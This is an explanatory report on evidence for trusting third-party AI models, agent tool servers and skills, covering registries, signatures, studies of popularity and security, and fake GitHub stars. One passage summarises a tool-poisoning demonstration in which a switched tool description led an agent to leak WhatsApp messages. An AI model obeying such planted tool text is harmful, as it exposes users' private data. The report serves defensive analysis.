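# Evidence for trusting third-party AI models, frameworks and tool servers

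## Components that AI agents depend on, and what counts as evidence about them

An AI agent is a program in which a language model decides what to do next and other software carries out the decision. The organisation that runs an agent seldom writes all of this software. It may download a trained model from one publisher, take a programming framework from another, and get connections to mail, databases or payment systems from a dozen more. Each of these is a component, meaning something a third party publishes that an agent runs or calls. Whoever chooses a component, whether a person or the agent, has to judge a stranger's work, usually from what a web page displays, such as a description, the publisher's name, or a count of stars or downloads. A trust signal is anything observable that people take as a reason to rely on a component. How much a trust signal is worth, if anything, depends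 on exactly what it is evidence of and how easily someone could have faked it.

### From a request to a running tool

Suppose a bookkeeper asks an agent which customers have overdue invoices. The invoices are in a database that the agent cannot yet access.

An AI agent relies on several components before it takes any action. The model arrives as weights, the learned numbers that make up a trained model, often from a site such as Hugging Face. Loader code reads the files, rebuilds the model in memory and runs it. Some file formats can carry program instructions that run during loading, so opening a model can mean running its publisher's code. A framework supplies the loop around the model, and is an ordinary software package from a catalogue such as PyPI (for Python) or npm (for JavaScript). It passes the user's question to the model, picks out any request for an action from the reply, and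 feeds the result of that action back to the model.

The agent needs a tool server to reach the database. This is a program that offers actions such as reading mail or running a query. Tool servers usually communicate with agents over the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a message format that the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024. According to the US National Security Agency (NSA) in *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), the model turns what the user wants into a structured request, a client library translates that into an MCP message, the server matches the message to one of its tools, and the result returns by the same route. The NSA lists as a risk that agents can call new tools while they run, so a person may never get to choose those tools.

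The agent now looks for a server in a registry, a public catalogue of components. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) project opened an official registry in September 2025, and its launch post (2025) calls the contents "self-reported information". *Same Name, Different Server* (Kraishan, 2026) counted 21,643 servers in the registry eleven months after it opened. The registry does check that whoever publishes under the name of a web domain or an account on the code-sharing site GitHub controls that domain or account. Its documentation leaves inspection of the code to the package catalogues that host it, such as npm and PyPI, and to the marketplaces that copy the registry's entries. The MCP Registry's moderation policy advises users to assume "minimal-to-no moderation" and states that the maintainers will not remove servers merely for having security vulnerabilities. If a marketplace copied the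 list in the belief that the registry had vetted it, each would be relying on the other to inspect the code. Other catalogues are stricter. For example, Anthropic's software directory policy provides for a review of each submission on entry and further reviews later.

Several servers in the registry offer database access. For each tool, the model receives a name, a description and an input format, all written by the publisher, and sometimes annotations about how the tool behaves. The March 2025 version of the Model Context Protocol specification requires client programs to treat those annotations as untrusted unless they come from trusted servers. This rule is sensible, but applying it requires already knowing which servers deserve trust.

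A remote server runs on its publisher's machines, and the agent sends it messages. A local server is a program that the user downloads and installs. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* warns that a local server runs with the same privileges as the agent's client software. The same document requires any client with one-click installation to show the exact command and wait for approval. Once the user approves, according to Kraishan's summary, the code behind the registry name can use the user's credentials, network position and file system. Here that means the database password and whatever else the password gives access to. Users often grant more access than the task needs. The NSA gives the example of a GitHub server to which users granted blanket access, so a malicious tool could read private repositories (the folders in which a project keeps its code) and publish their contents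 in public ones.

The November 2025 version of the Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a human always be able to refuse a tool call, but it does not require a particular interface for this. A bookkeeper may see a dialog with the words "run query?" and press yes, but that approval is not evidence that the program running the query can be trusted.

The agent could also have gained its new ability from a skill, which is a folder of written instructions. The official Agent Skills *Specification* requires only one text file, and scripts, reference documents and other resources are optional. According to Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (2025), the agent loads the name and description of every installed skill at startup and reads the rest when a task seems to call for it. The publisher's wording therefore helps determine when the agent uses the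 skill. *Context Matters* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026) found at least one script in 44.1% of the skills on the marketplace ClawHub, compared with 12 to 16% in its other sources. A skill without scripts can still do damage, because the agent may follow its instructions with all the access that the user has granted. Anthropic advises installing skills only from trusted sources and thoroughly auditing any others, but few bookkeepers can do such an audit.

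### Seven properties behind the word "safe"

Asking whether the database server is safe combines several questions. It helps to consider them separately, because each concerns a different kind of failure.

| Property | How it fails |
|---|---|
| The publisher is who it seems to be | Impersonation: an attacker uses a confusable name or takes over an abandoned one |
| The file is unaltered | Hijacked release: an intruder replaces the file after publication |
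| The publisher built the file from the stated source | Hijacked release: an intruder adds code during the build that the public source does not contain |
| The code is not malicious | Hidden behaviour: the author wrote the code to steal or destroy |
| The component has no serious flaws | Careless flaw: an honest mistake lets outsiders in |
| The component behaves as described | Hidden behaviour: the weights react to a secret trigger, or a tool does more than its description admits |
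| All of this will stay true | Later change: an update, or a remote server's operator, alters what the user approved |

A component can come unaltered from its stated publisher and still be unsafe. MCP Inspector, a program for testing tool servers under development, accepted unverified inputs through which an attacker could run commands on the developer's machine. The NSA cites this flaw, CVE-2025-49596, which version 0.14.1 fixed. An attacker didn't need to impersonate the publisher or tamper with the file, so verifying the program's origin would not have protected a user.

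A skill's listing can look normal even after the identity of its owner has changed. Some marketplaces store the skills they offer, but others, such as Skills.sh, only point to folders in other people's GitHub repositories. Holzbauer and colleagues found seven abandoned repositories that skill indexes still pointed to, and showed that an attacker could take them over. This would have affected 121 skills, one with more than 1,000 recorded installations, without changing their index entries.

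A tool server can change after a user approves it, and the NSA describes a demonstration of this with the messaging application WhatsApp. Researchers connected an agent to a trusted WhatsApp server and to a malicious server of their own, whose tool descriptions led the agent to disclose the user's messages. The malicious server showed a harmless description at installation and switched to the harmful one after its second use, so a user who read everything carefully before approving it would have found nothing to object to.

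Model weights need separate treatment because they may contain no program code. A model can pass every search for malicious code and still have a backdoor, which is hidden behaviour that appears only under conditions its maker chose. Whether the code is malicious and whether the component behaves as described are therefore separate questions for a model, though they amount to the same question for a small script.

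### Hashes, signatures and attestations

Much of the technical evidence about components rests on a few cryptographic tools, and each of them establishes less than its reputation suggests.

A hash is a short fingerprint that anyone can compute from a file. Changing a single character of the file changes the hash, and nobody knows a practical way to make two different files share a hash computed with a modern method. Matching hashes therefore show that two files are the same, but not whether the file is any good. A hash on the same web page as the download also gives little protection against an intruder who can edit that page.

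A signer computes a digital signature from a file and a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check it. A valid signature shows that someone in control of the private key approved that exact file. It doesn't show whether that person is honest, competent or the rightful owner of the key.

An attestation is a signed statement about a file, which it identifies by hash. A build service might attest that it produced the file from a particular version of the source code, or a laboratory might attest that it ran a particular test and got a certain result. The signature protects the statement from alteration, but readers still have to trust that the signer was in a position to know the facts and reported them correctly.

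### When a signal is checkable

A trust signal is checkable if it makes a definite claim about an identified artifact and someone other than the producer can test that claim. "Secure and production-ready" is not a definite claim. "Our server opens no connections except to your database" is definite, but unless the publisher names a version, preferably by hash, it can dismiss any other connection a tester finds by saying the tester had the wrong copy. "Our internal team reviewed file X and found no problems" identifies the artifact, but outsiders can't repeat the review. Star counts are weak signals by this standard. Anyone can confirm that a repository has 4,000 stars, but the stars don't apply to a specific release, and people may have given them for reasons ranging from admiration to wanting to read the code later.

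How hard evidence is to fake is separate from whether it can be checked. An expensive advertising campaign is hard to fake but makes no testable claim about any file. The statement about database connections, with a hash added, is fully checkable but just as easy to write if it is false. The MCP registry's name check shows how the two properties combine. The check makes it hard to publish under a bank's existing domain but does little to stop someone who registers a similar one.

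A checkable claim also protects nobody until somebody checks it.

### The likelihood ratio

How far should a signal change someone's opinion? Probability theory gives the answer as a ratio:

likelihood ratio = P(signal if bad) / P(signal if good)

The odds that a component is bad, given the signal, are the odds before seeing it multiplied by this ratio. The signal is a warning if the ratio is above 1, reassuring if it is below 1, and uninformative if it is exactly 1.

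Suppose a hypothetical registry has 1,000 tool servers, of which 50 are malicious and 950 honest, and 80% of each group have a polished description. A user who excludes the 200 servers without one is left with 760 honest servers and 40 malicious ones. That is 5% malicious, the same as in the whole registry, so in this example a polished description is no evidence that a server is honest.

If only 20% of the malicious servers had polished descriptions, the ratio would be 0.2/0.8, or one quarter. The user would keep 760 honest servers and 10 malicious ones, and the malicious share would fall to 1.3%. The ratio can also exceed one. Suppose attackers put more effort into appearances than honest hobbyists do, so that 96% of malicious servers and 48% of honest ones look polished. The user would then keep 504 servers, 48 of them malicious, so choosing only polished servers would nearly double the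 malicious share, to 9.5%.

The ratio depends on what "bad" means. A valid signature from a known company should be rare among impostors, but it may be just as common among carelessly written servers as among well-written ones. It can therefore be strong evidence about identity and no evidence about flaws. Evidence that can be checked doesn't always have a useful ratio either. For example, a thief can truthfully attest that a malicious program was built from its published source.

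### Why cheap signals decay

In the example, polish stopped being useful evidence once malicious publishers could produce it as easily as honest ones. *Job Market Signaling* (Spence, 1973) gives the general condition, using a model in which an employer cannot see how productive job applicants are and has to judge them by observable traits. Spence calls traits that applicants cannot change indices, and traits they can change, such as education, signals. A signal can separate good applicants from bad only if the good ones can acquire it more easily.

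His numerical example has two groups. Members of Group I are worth 1 to the employer and members of Group II are worth 2. An amount y of education costs Group I y and Group II only y/2. The employer pays 2 to anyone with at least y* of education and 1 to everyone else. Group I goes without education if 1 > 2 − y*, which means y* > 1. Group II gets it if 2 − y*/2 > 1, which means y* < 2. For any threshold between 1 and 2, only Group II gets the education, so experience confirms the employer's belief. At y* = 1.5, education would leave a member of Group I with 0.5, less than the wage of 1 available without it, but it leaves a member of Group II with 1.25.

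If education becomes ten times cheaper for both groups, the old threshold fails because everyone can afford it, but the employer can restore the sorting by asking for between 10 and 20 units instead. If a diploma mill charges both groups the same y/10, no threshold works, because any level that deters Group I also deters Group II. A fall in price alone therefore need not ruin a signal, which fails when the weaker group can acquire it for less than it brings in.

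Shen, Sood and Weitzel (2026), in *Social Proof is in the Pudding*, apply this reasoning to GitHub stars, which vendors have sold for as little as ten cents each. Bad projects still pay more for stars than good ones, which may earn them for free. But a thousand stars at that price cost $100, which is little compared with what stolen company credentials may be worth, so the condition that should keep impostors out fails. Shen and colleagues add that users can grow wary without knowing the price, after finding that a few highly starred projects are poor. They also doubt that wariness is a full defence, since 500 stars may impress even a sceptic more than 5 do.

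Online labour markets provide measured evidence that good writing loses value as a signal when AI makes it easy to produce. Cui, Dias and Ye (2025), in *Signaling in the Age of AI*, studied a platform that gave some workers an AI tool for writing cover letters. Letters became better tailored to the job, but the correlation between tailoring and a reply from the employer fell by 52%, and employers turned to work histories instead. Galdin and Silbert (2025), in *Making Talk Cheap*, used data from Freelancer.com to simulate a market in which written applications carry no information about ability. In it, the most able fifth of workers were hired 19% less often than before language models arrived, and the least able fifth 14% more often. Hiring differs from software selection, and the second result is simulated. Still, AI can write a tool server's description as easily as a cover letter, so there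 is little reason to expect well-written descriptions in a registry to remain useful evidence.

Software is a harder case than hiring as Spence describes it, where the employer eventually learns how productive each worker is and corrects mistaken beliefs. Someone whose password leaks may never learn which component leaked it, so people can go on trusting a worthless signal for longer. Spence also assumes that applicants enter the market too rarely to build a reputation for honest signalling. That assumption fits an attacker with a disposable account better than a company that has published software for ten years and stands to lose its customers.

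Outside testing can make a false claim about a file harder to sustain than a true one. Any publisher can easily write that a file with a given hash connects only to the user's database. If outsiders routinely run the file and watch its connections, an honest publisher has no extra work to do, but a thief must either give up sending data out that way or find a way past the test. The claim's value as evidence then depends on how hard the test is to evade.

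## Whether popular components are more secure

The usual reason for preferring a popular component is that other people have already checked it. Programmers call this the "many eyes" argument, or Linus's law, after a slogan that any bug is easy to find if enough people look. *Increased security through open source* (2008) sets it out in full. Anyone can read open source code, different users notice different flaws, and some send corrections to the project, so everyone who updates gets the fixes. Developers may also write more carefully when they know strangers will read their work.

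Choosing the tool server with the most stars on these grounds requires several further assumptions. The star count has to reflect how many people use the server, some of those users have to inspect the code and find its flaws, and somebody has to fix them. Popular and obscure servers also have to be alike in other ways, because a popular server that began with ten times as many flaws as an obscure one could have most of them fixed and still be the worse choice.

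### Stars, downloads and actual use

People can star a project without using it. Koch, Klein and Johns (2024), in *The Fault in Our Stars*, compared stars with downloads for 925,978 PHP, Ruby and JavaScript projects. On a scale from 0 (no relationship) to 1, the association was 0.47 for PHP, 0.33 for Ruby and 0.14 for JavaScript. About a fifth of the Ruby projects and a quarter of the PHP projects had many downloads but few stars. Koch and colleagues suspect that these are small utilities that other packages install automatically, so developers hardly notice them.

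Downloads are an imperfect measure too, since automated build systems fetch the same package repeatedly. Koch and colleagues therefore also looked for software in use. They wrote tests to recognise 58 JavaScript libraries and ran them on the 100,000 most popular websites, of which about 71% loaded. The number of sites using a library had an association of 0.61 with its stars and 0.63 with its downloads. Stars are therefore a fair guide to use for these libraries, but the sample is small and the method covers only code that can be detected in a visitor's browser, which excludes a tool server running on somebody's laptop.

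Some packages link to a secondary repository or to another project's, so the star count can misrepresent their popularity. The npm entry for Highcharts, a charting library with 165 million downloads, pointed to a secondary repository with 203 stars, while the main one had 11,683. A Ruby package with 1,953 downloads listed React's repository as its source, though React is a JavaScript library with nearly 217,000 stars and no Ruby code.

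### From users to inspectors to fixes

*Is Parallel Programming Hard* (2017), a programming textbook, asks how many people will actually look at a given piece of code, and how many of them are able to find its bugs. Imtiaz and Williams (2022) partly answer this in *Are your dependencies code reviewed?*. They took the 1,000 most downloaded packages in each of four registries and checked whether the changes in each package's last ten updates had been code reviewed. In 52.5% of cases, the review covered only part of the update, and only 9.0% of the packages had complete review for all the updates studied. Popularity clearly doesn't guarantee code review, but it may still make review more likely, since the study had no unpopular packages for comparison.

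Popular projects also attract people who edit the code, and more editors can make more mistakes. *Vulnerability Detection in Open Source Software* (2022) cites a study in which files changed by nine or more developers were 16 times as likely to have a vulnerability as other files. This is weak evidence against Linus's law, since files that many people edit are probably larger and more complicated to begin with.

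Security researchers tend to inspect popular projects. According to Koch and colleagues, they prefer to use stars to choose what to test. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) ranked tool server projects by stars, kept 100, and found 25 security advisories and 147 security-related issues in their repositories. Obscure servers may get no such attention. Even for the whole protocol, *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) has only 24 validated vulnerabilities in its dataset, 14 of them critical, and describes discovery as being at an early stage. With so few confirmed flaws among thousands of servers, the absence of a report is very weak evidence that any one of them is secure.

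People may also keep using a model after its flaws are found and made public. Nguyen, Le and Babar (2026), in *Vulnerable Models in the AI Supply Chain*, traced 16,977 Hugging Face models that a public database lists as unsafe, and found 3,757 of them named in the code of thousands of GitHub projects. One of these, a small model for classifying the sentiment of text, had over 655,000 downloads and appeared in 449 repositories, despite a warning that loading it could run hidden code. Other people had trained 24 new models from it, and only four of those had moved to a safer file format. Some of the warnings may be false alarms, and Hugging Face publishes the flagged model with the most references for automated tests.

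Some components have nobody left to fix them. Guo, Hao and colleagues (2025), in *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem*, found that 21.9% of 8,060 tool servers had gone more than a year without an update. Earlier research that He, Kapravelos and colleagues (2026) review in *Six Million (Suspected) Fake Stars on GitHub* found that GitHub stars do not predict whether an open source project will last, so they are little help in spotting such projects in advance.

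### A census of tool servers

Kraishan's September 2026 census of the MCP registry skips these intermediate steps and asks whether servers with more stars have fewer weaknesses. Of the 21,643 registered servers, Kraishan obtained source code for 14,353. Most of the rest listed no GitHub repository, or one that no longer existed. A scanner then searched the code for 31 patterns in eight classes of weakness. Kraishan rated four classes as high severity:

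- instructions to the model hidden in a tool's description
- passing a user's credentials on to another service
- running commands built from unchecked input
- accepting network connections without authentication

The other four were excessive permissions, careless handling of passwords and keys, fetching web addresses without checking them, and relying on other packages without specifying exact versions.

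The scanner flagged 15.2% of the servers for at least one weakness and 11.1% for a high-severity one. Of the 1,599 servers in the high-severity group, 1,373 had the authentication problem, which is often caused by a single unsafe setting. The scanner detected no hidden instructions in any server. The census is therefore evidence about carelessness, not about whether popular servers are less likely to be malicious.

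The number of stars had almost no relationship with the number of findings. The rank correlation was 0.008, on a scale from −1 (opposite orderings) to 1 (identical orderings), where 0 means the orderings are unrelated.

Kraishan also sorted the servers by stars into ten equal groups. The share with a high-severity finding peaked at 18.6% in the second-lowest group, rose and fell through the middle, and was lowest, at 7.5%, in the top group. But 7,156 of the scanned servers, almost exactly half, have no stars, so the four lowest groups and nearly all of the fifth must consist of servers tied at zero. The second group is therefore no more popular than the first, which rules out Kraishan's suggestion that servers near the bottom may have enough visibility to attract users but too little to attract reviewers. The peak must have another cause, perhaps the order in which the tied servers were listed.

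The low figure for the top group doesn't have this problem. The combined figure for the other nine groups is about 11.5%, so being in the top tenth has a likelihood ratio of about 0.65 for high-severity findings, which is only mildly reassuring.

### How a zero correlation and a protective effect can both hold

Kraishan then fitted a logistic regression, a model that estimates how each of several characteristics changes the odds of a high-severity finding when the others stay the same. The model uses the natural logarithm of one plus the number of stars, and each unit of it multiplies the odds by 0.78. For a server with 1,000 stars the logarithm is about 6.9, so the multiplier is:

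0.78^6.9 ≈ 0.18

Under the model, this server's odds of a high-severity finding are therefore less than a fifth of those of an otherwise identical zero-star server. If the zero-star server had an 11% chance of such a finding, the popular one would have about a 2% chance.

Popular servers also tend to be larger. Each one-unit increase in the logarithm of the number of files multiplies the odds by 1.94. In the model, a server with 1,000 stars and 39 files has the same odds as one with no stars and two files. More code leaves more room for both mistakes and false alarms from a scanner. Skills seem to follow a similar pattern. *Agent Skills in the Wild* (2026) examined 31,132 skills and found that the odds of a vulnerability were 2.12 times as high for those with scripts as for those containing only instructions.

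An invented example shows how size can hide a protective effect. The table gives the number of servers with a serious weakness.

| | Small servers | Large servers | All servers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Obscure | 64 of 800 (8%) | 36 of 200 (18%) | 100 of 1,000 (10%) |
| Popular | 12 of 200 (6%) | 88 of 800 (11%) | 100 of 1,000 (10%) |

The popular servers do better in both size classes, but the totals are identical because most popular servers are large. In the census, the correlation and the regression also use different measures. The correlation uses the number of findings of any severity, while the regression uses only whether a server has at least one high-severity finding.

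Someone choosing between two servers of similar size and age could reasonably give stars a little weight, but stars are likely to be much less useful for ranking the whole registry, because its servers vary widely in size.

Even the 0.78 may be too favourable to popular servers. Kraishan fetched at most 40 files from each repository, so a project with 4,000 files is measured as no larger than one with 40, and most of its code is not scanned. If popular projects exceed the limit more often, they appear safer partly because more of their code was left unscanned.

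The model as a whole explains little, with a pseudo-R² of 0.05, where 0 means that the characteristics add nothing to knowing the overall rate. Neither maintenance within the last 180 days nor the presence of a licence had an effect that Kraishan could distinguish from zero (odds ratios of 1.22 and 1.01). The test of maintenance was weak, though, because half of the repositories had changed within about 16 days of the census and few servers were old enough to look neglected. Archived repositories, which their owners have closed to further changes, had 1.52 times the odds of a high-severity finding, and older repositories also did worse. Servers with a history of silent changes to their listings had nearly three times the odds, a stronger warning sign than any of these.

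One author produced these results and was the only person to check the scanner's accuracy, judging only a little over half of the sampled findings to be real. If false alarms were equally common among popular and obscure servers, they would make any real difference between the two groups look smaller, so the near-zero correlation does not prove that popularity has no effect.

### Packages, skills, models and cloud settings

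Studies of other software disagree about whether popular components are more secure, partly because they measure security in different ways. The earliest direct test, *Is Popularity an Indicator of Software Security?* (Siavvas, Jankovic and colleagues, 2018), ranked 20 Java libraries by downloads and by potential flaws per thousand lines of code. The correlation was −0.17, which they interpret as popular libraries being slightly less secure, but it was far from statistically significant. With 20 libraries, a correlation would need to be around 0.45 in either direction to reach the usual threshold for significance. All 20 were among the most popular Java libraries, so the study could not compare them with obscure ones.

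*The Popularity Hypothesis in Software Security* (Ruohonen and Ramadan, 2025) compares 381,993 PHP packages. The 777 with at least one reported vulnerability had more installations, stars and dependent packages on average than the rest. This difference may reflect closer inspection of popular packages rather than worse security, because someone must find a flaw before it can be reported. Suppose a popular package has two flaws and an obscure one has four, and inspectors report half of the flaws in the first but only 5% of those in the second. The popular package would average one report and the obscure one 0.2, even though the popular package has half as many flaws. Ruohonen and Ramadan doubt that the 381,216 packages without reported vulnerabilities are free of flaws.

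The clearest evidence that popular projects are more secure comes from cloud computing. *Exploring Security Practices in Infrastructure as Code* (Verdet and colleagues, 2023) examined 401 public projects that use Terraform, a tool for describing servers, networks and permissions in text files, to set up services on Amazon's cloud. A scanner checked the files against recognised security rules. Projects with two stars passed 69% of the checks on average, those with 20 to 49 stars passed 83%, and those with 800 to 1,499 passed 98%, but the average fell to 64% for the five projects with the most stars.

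Popularity may look better here than in the census because Verdet and colleagues recorded the share of checks that a project passed, so a large project did not score worse merely for having more settings to check. The rules are also public and a free tool can test them, so a passing user can spot and correct violations. Review by many users may work well for problems on a known checklist and less well for subtle ones. However, the two highest groups contain only nine and five projects, so neither the 98% nor the drop after it is very reliable.

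*Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) used language models to examine 6,309 skills from two marketplaces for signs of harmful intent. On skillsmp, which displays stars, the models flagged 5.8% of skills in the lowest popularity band, 7.4% in the middle and 6.6% in the highest. On ClawHub, which displays downloads, the figures fell from 4.6% to 2.9% and then 2.0%, although only the difference between the lowest and highest bands was statistically clear. If the download counts were genuine, a ClawHub user choosing from the highest band would meet fewer than half as many flagged skills as one choosing from the lowest. About a third of the flagged skills across both marketplaces were openly published hacking tools rather than disguised malware, and the study deliberately excluded the very most popular skills.

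The same study measured how much damage a skill could do, whatever its author intended. The share of skills with a notable risk of damage rose with popularity on both marketplaces, from 35.5% to 42.6% on skillsmp and from 62.4% to 69.6% on ClawHub. Pandey and colleagues' explanation is that widely adopted skills do more. For example, a skill that reads files and sends messages is more useful than a style guide, but more dangerous if something goes wrong.

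The many-eyes argument applies poorly to model weights, because users cannot spot a mistake by reading billions of numbers. They can, however, see the file format. *PickleBall* (2025) examined Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month and found that 21% of models came only in pickle, a format that can run code when a program loads it. The same was true of 29 of the 100 most downloaded models. A pickle file is not necessarily malicious, but heavy use had evidently not pushed publishers towards safer formats.

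### Why wide use attracts attackers

Everything that makes a component attractive to users also makes it attractive to someone who wants to reach those users. Suppose an attacker expects to gain an amount v from each installation of a component, and the component has n installations. Getting a malicious version into it costs c. The attack pays if:

n × v > c

If an attacker earns one dollar per installation and the attack costs $10,000, a component with 5,000 installations is not worth attacking, but one with 500,000 is. Better defences can offset the appeal of the larger target, but in this example they would have to make the attack 50 times as expensive.

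A component's value to an attacker depends on indirect installations as well as direct ones. An average npm package implicitly trusts 79 packages from other people, according to research cited in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (2026). A small utility with hardly any stars can therefore run on a huge number of machines, and neither its users nor its maintainer could tell from the star count that it was a valuable target. Guo and colleagues found that tool servers written in Java overwhelmingly rely on one framework, Spring, so a single flaw there could affect many servers at once.

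Attackers target established packages. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (2026) reconstructs 12 incidents in which they used stolen credentials to publish malicious versions of existing packages, from eslint-scope in 2018 to axios in 2026. The incidents involved 41 malicious releases of 15 packages. The researchers selected these cases from public write-ups, so they don't show how much more often these attacks hit popular packages than obscure ones.

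Past inspection does not protect users in such a case. They may have read earlier versions closely for years, but the thief's release is new to all of them, and it appears beside the stars and downloads from those earlier versions. With many users, somebody may notice the problem sooner, which helps people who install the package later but not those who have already run the thief's release.

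## How stars, likes and download counts are faked

A GitHub star shows only that someone logged in to an account and clicked a button. A Hugging Face like works in much the same way. Each account can star a project only once, so a thousand fake stars require a thousand accounts.

A download count records even less. It shows only that a computer requested a file, and the same computer can request it again. PyPI logs the type of program that made each request, and some of these programs are known bots, including one that copies packages to mirror sites. A package can therefore collect downloads without anyone choosing it. Excluding known bots doesn't solve the problem, because a script can also produce downloads that appear human. In an experiment, Shen and colleagues used one to raise the median number of apparently human downloads for a random set of Python packages from about 20 to 100.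 In *How Reliable Are FOSS Popularity Metrics?*, Swierzy, Pohl and colleagues (2025) looked for a rule that npm counts each network address only once a day and found none.

Some rankings instead count how many other packages depend on a component. This count can also be faked, because anyone can publish packages on npm. In 2024 a scheme called tea began offering maintainers rewards based on how much other software relied on theirs. Swierzy and colleagues later identified 71,710 npm packages, about 2% of the registry, that seemed to exist only to inflate this measure. They checked 100 of them by hand and found none wrongly identified. Of the 1,000 npm packages with the most direct dependents, 532 were among the packages they identified.

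### What a thousand stars cost

Ten cents a star is near the bottom of the market. In July 2024, He and colleagues found other sellers charging up to $2.00, so 1,000 stars can cost from $100 to $2,000. Part of the price difference reflects how long the stars last. Swierzy and colleagues cite a 2023 report in which stars at €0.08 came from automatically created accounts, which GitHub removed within a month, while stars at €0.80 came from accounts that were harder to recognise as fake. The cheaper stars may be enough for someone who needs to look popular for only a week.

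Shen and colleagues bought 50 stars for each of 25 new Python packages in May 2023. The seller delivered the stars over a few days, all from accounts created around 20 April, about three weeks before the purchase.

Some fake stars come from accounts that sellers don't own. He et al. also describe groups whose members star each other's projects, and companies that give gifts to people who star theirs. GitHub's rules forbid all of this, but these stars are much harder to detect because they can come from real people with ordinary accounts.

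### How StarScout detects suspicious stars

He et al. built a program, StarScout, to search for two suspicious patterns in public records of 326 million stars given between July 2019 and December 2024.

StarScout's low-activity signature is an account that has starred one repository and taken at most one other action, in the same repository on the same day. Real people sometimes behave like this too, for example when they register, star a friend's project and never return. StarScout therefore ignores these stars unless a repository has at least 50 of them. The threshold is 50 because sellers often set that as their minimum order.

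The lockstep signature is a group of accounts that repeatedly star the same projects at about the same time. A seller who controls a limited number of accounts and promises quick delivery will tend to produce this pattern. A group of accounts U and a group of repositories R are in lockstep if:

|U| ≥ n and |R| ≥ m, and

for every repository in R, at least ρ × n accounts in U starred it within some period of length Δt

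StarScout looks for groups of at least 50 accounts and 10 repositories in which each repository received stars from at least 25 of the accounts within 30 days (n = 50, m = 10, ρ = 0.5, Δt = 30 days).

A smaller example uses n = 4, m = 3 and the same ρ and Δt, so each repository needs two stars from the group within 30 days. Suppose Ann and Bob star repository X in March, Bob and Cem star Y in April, and Cem and Dee star Z in June. The four accounts are in lockstep, although none starred all three repositories. With numbers this small, the pattern could easily be a coincidence, so the real thresholds are much higher.

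Checking every possible group of accounts would take far too long, so StarScout uses CopyCatch, a method Facebook deployed against fake likes. CopyCatch starts from a few repositories and repeatedly adjusts the time window to find the largest suspicious group around them. It is fast but can miss groups.

The two signatures together flagged 6.0 million stars in 26,254 repositories, 4.93 million of them through lockstep. Many of these repositories had probably not bought anything. Fake accounts also star well-known projects, apparently to look normal, so a famous project can collect fake stars without its owners' involvement. A post-processing step therefore keeps a repository only if it meets two conditions:

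- in at least one month it received more than 50 suspected fake stars, and these made up more than half of that month's stars
- suspected fakes make up more than 10% of all its stars

After post-processing, 18,617 repositories had suspected fake-star campaigns, involving about 301,000 accounts and 3.81 million stars. The widely quoted figure of six million stars is from before post-processing.

### What the suspected repositories were

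By January 2025, 90.42% of the 18,617 repositories had disappeared from GitHub. Their contents were no longer available, but many had names suggesting pirated software, game cheats or cryptocurrency bots. He et al. infer that most were disguised malware, partly because surviving repositories with similar names were malware. One of these survivors had 111 stars, at least 109 of them suspected fakes, and claimed to be a blockchain application but contained code that stole cryptocurrency.

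He and colleagues also classified 580 of the surviving repositories. Spam and malware made up 22.6%, and AI projects were the next largest group at 16.6%. Many of the AI projects were code for academic papers or start-ups' products. A start-up may buy stars to impress investors, so a suspicious star count is a reason to examine a component more closely, but it does not show that the component is malicious.

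Suspected fake stars never exceeded about 1% of all stars given in a month, but in July 2024, 16.66% of the repositories that received at least 50 stars had a suspected fake-star campaign. Only 229 of the 18,617 repositories with suspected campaigns were linked to a package that programmers could install from a registry. The security company Socket added StarScout's results to its product and found such packages in 283 of two million customer bills of materials, which are machine-readable lists of the parts in a piece of software.

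### How accurate StarScout is

He et al. tested StarScout on a known malware campaign that had used 847 repositories and 15,672 suspicious accounts. The tool found 81% of the repositories and 76% of the accounts. This test is weaker evidence of how well it detects stars bought by start-ups, which may use different sellers and have more genuine stars mixed in.

It is harder to tell how many of the flagged repositories really had fake stars, because nobody outside the trade has a list of the repositories that bought them, so He and colleagues compared deletion rates. Only 5% of a random sample of repositories with at least 50 stars had disappeared, against 90% of those with suspected campaigns. The figures for accounts were 3.5% and 57%. However, GitHub may delete a repository for malware or copyright violations whether or not anyone paid for its stars. He and colleagues note that even if 99%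 of the flagged repositories were correctly identified, about 180 would be falsely accused, and that StarScout's evidence is not enough to justify punishing anyone.

StarScout misses small purchases. The 50 stars that Shen and colleagues bought for each package would not be enough on their own to meet its post-processing threshold of more than 50. It is also likely to miss stars that real people gave in return for a gift or favour, unless those people repeatedly act together. Some of the accounts it catches look fairly convincing. About 15% of those in suspected campaigns also created repositories and uploaded code, and He and colleagues couldn't always tell from the profiles whether a real person was behind them.

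Looking for sudden bursts of stars has the opposite weakness of sometimes flagging real stars, since real enthusiasm also comes in bursts. *Adoption and Ecosystem Health* (2026), a study of frameworks for building groups of AI agents, flags a star if it meets at least two of three conditions: the account is new, its profile is empty, or the project received at least 50 stars in the same hour. If a popular video sends thousands of beginners to GitHub, their stars could meet all three.

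### A malicious model at the top of Hugging Face

In May 2026, the repository Open-OSS/privacy-filter reached first place on Hugging Face's trending list. It imitated a real OpenAI model, including its description, and contained a program that stole passwords and cryptocurrency wallets from Windows computers. The AI security company HiddenLayer reports in *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) that the repository collected about 244,000 downloads and 667 likes in under 18 hours. The company considers both numbers almost certainly inflated.

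The names of the accounts that liked it are good evidence for this. Of the 667 accounts, 504 had names made up of a first name, a last name and three digits, and 153 had names made up of an adjective, a noun and four digits. Only 10 followed neither pattern. Plenty of real people choose names like these, but it is very unlikely that 98.5% of the real users who liked a model would. Some of the accounts also followed another publisher, whose six repositories contained nearly the same malicious program.

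The 244,000 downloads don't measure the number of victims. They averaged more than 13,500 an hour, and scripts may have made most of them. Even a genuine download did not infect a computer unless the user ran the program, and the attack failed on Mac and Linux.

A method like StarScout's would have been too slow to help here. It compares months of activity, and its designers suggest adding new data every quarter, but this repository reached first place in less than a day. Hugging Face removed the repository after HiddenLayer reported it.

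### ClawHub's download counter

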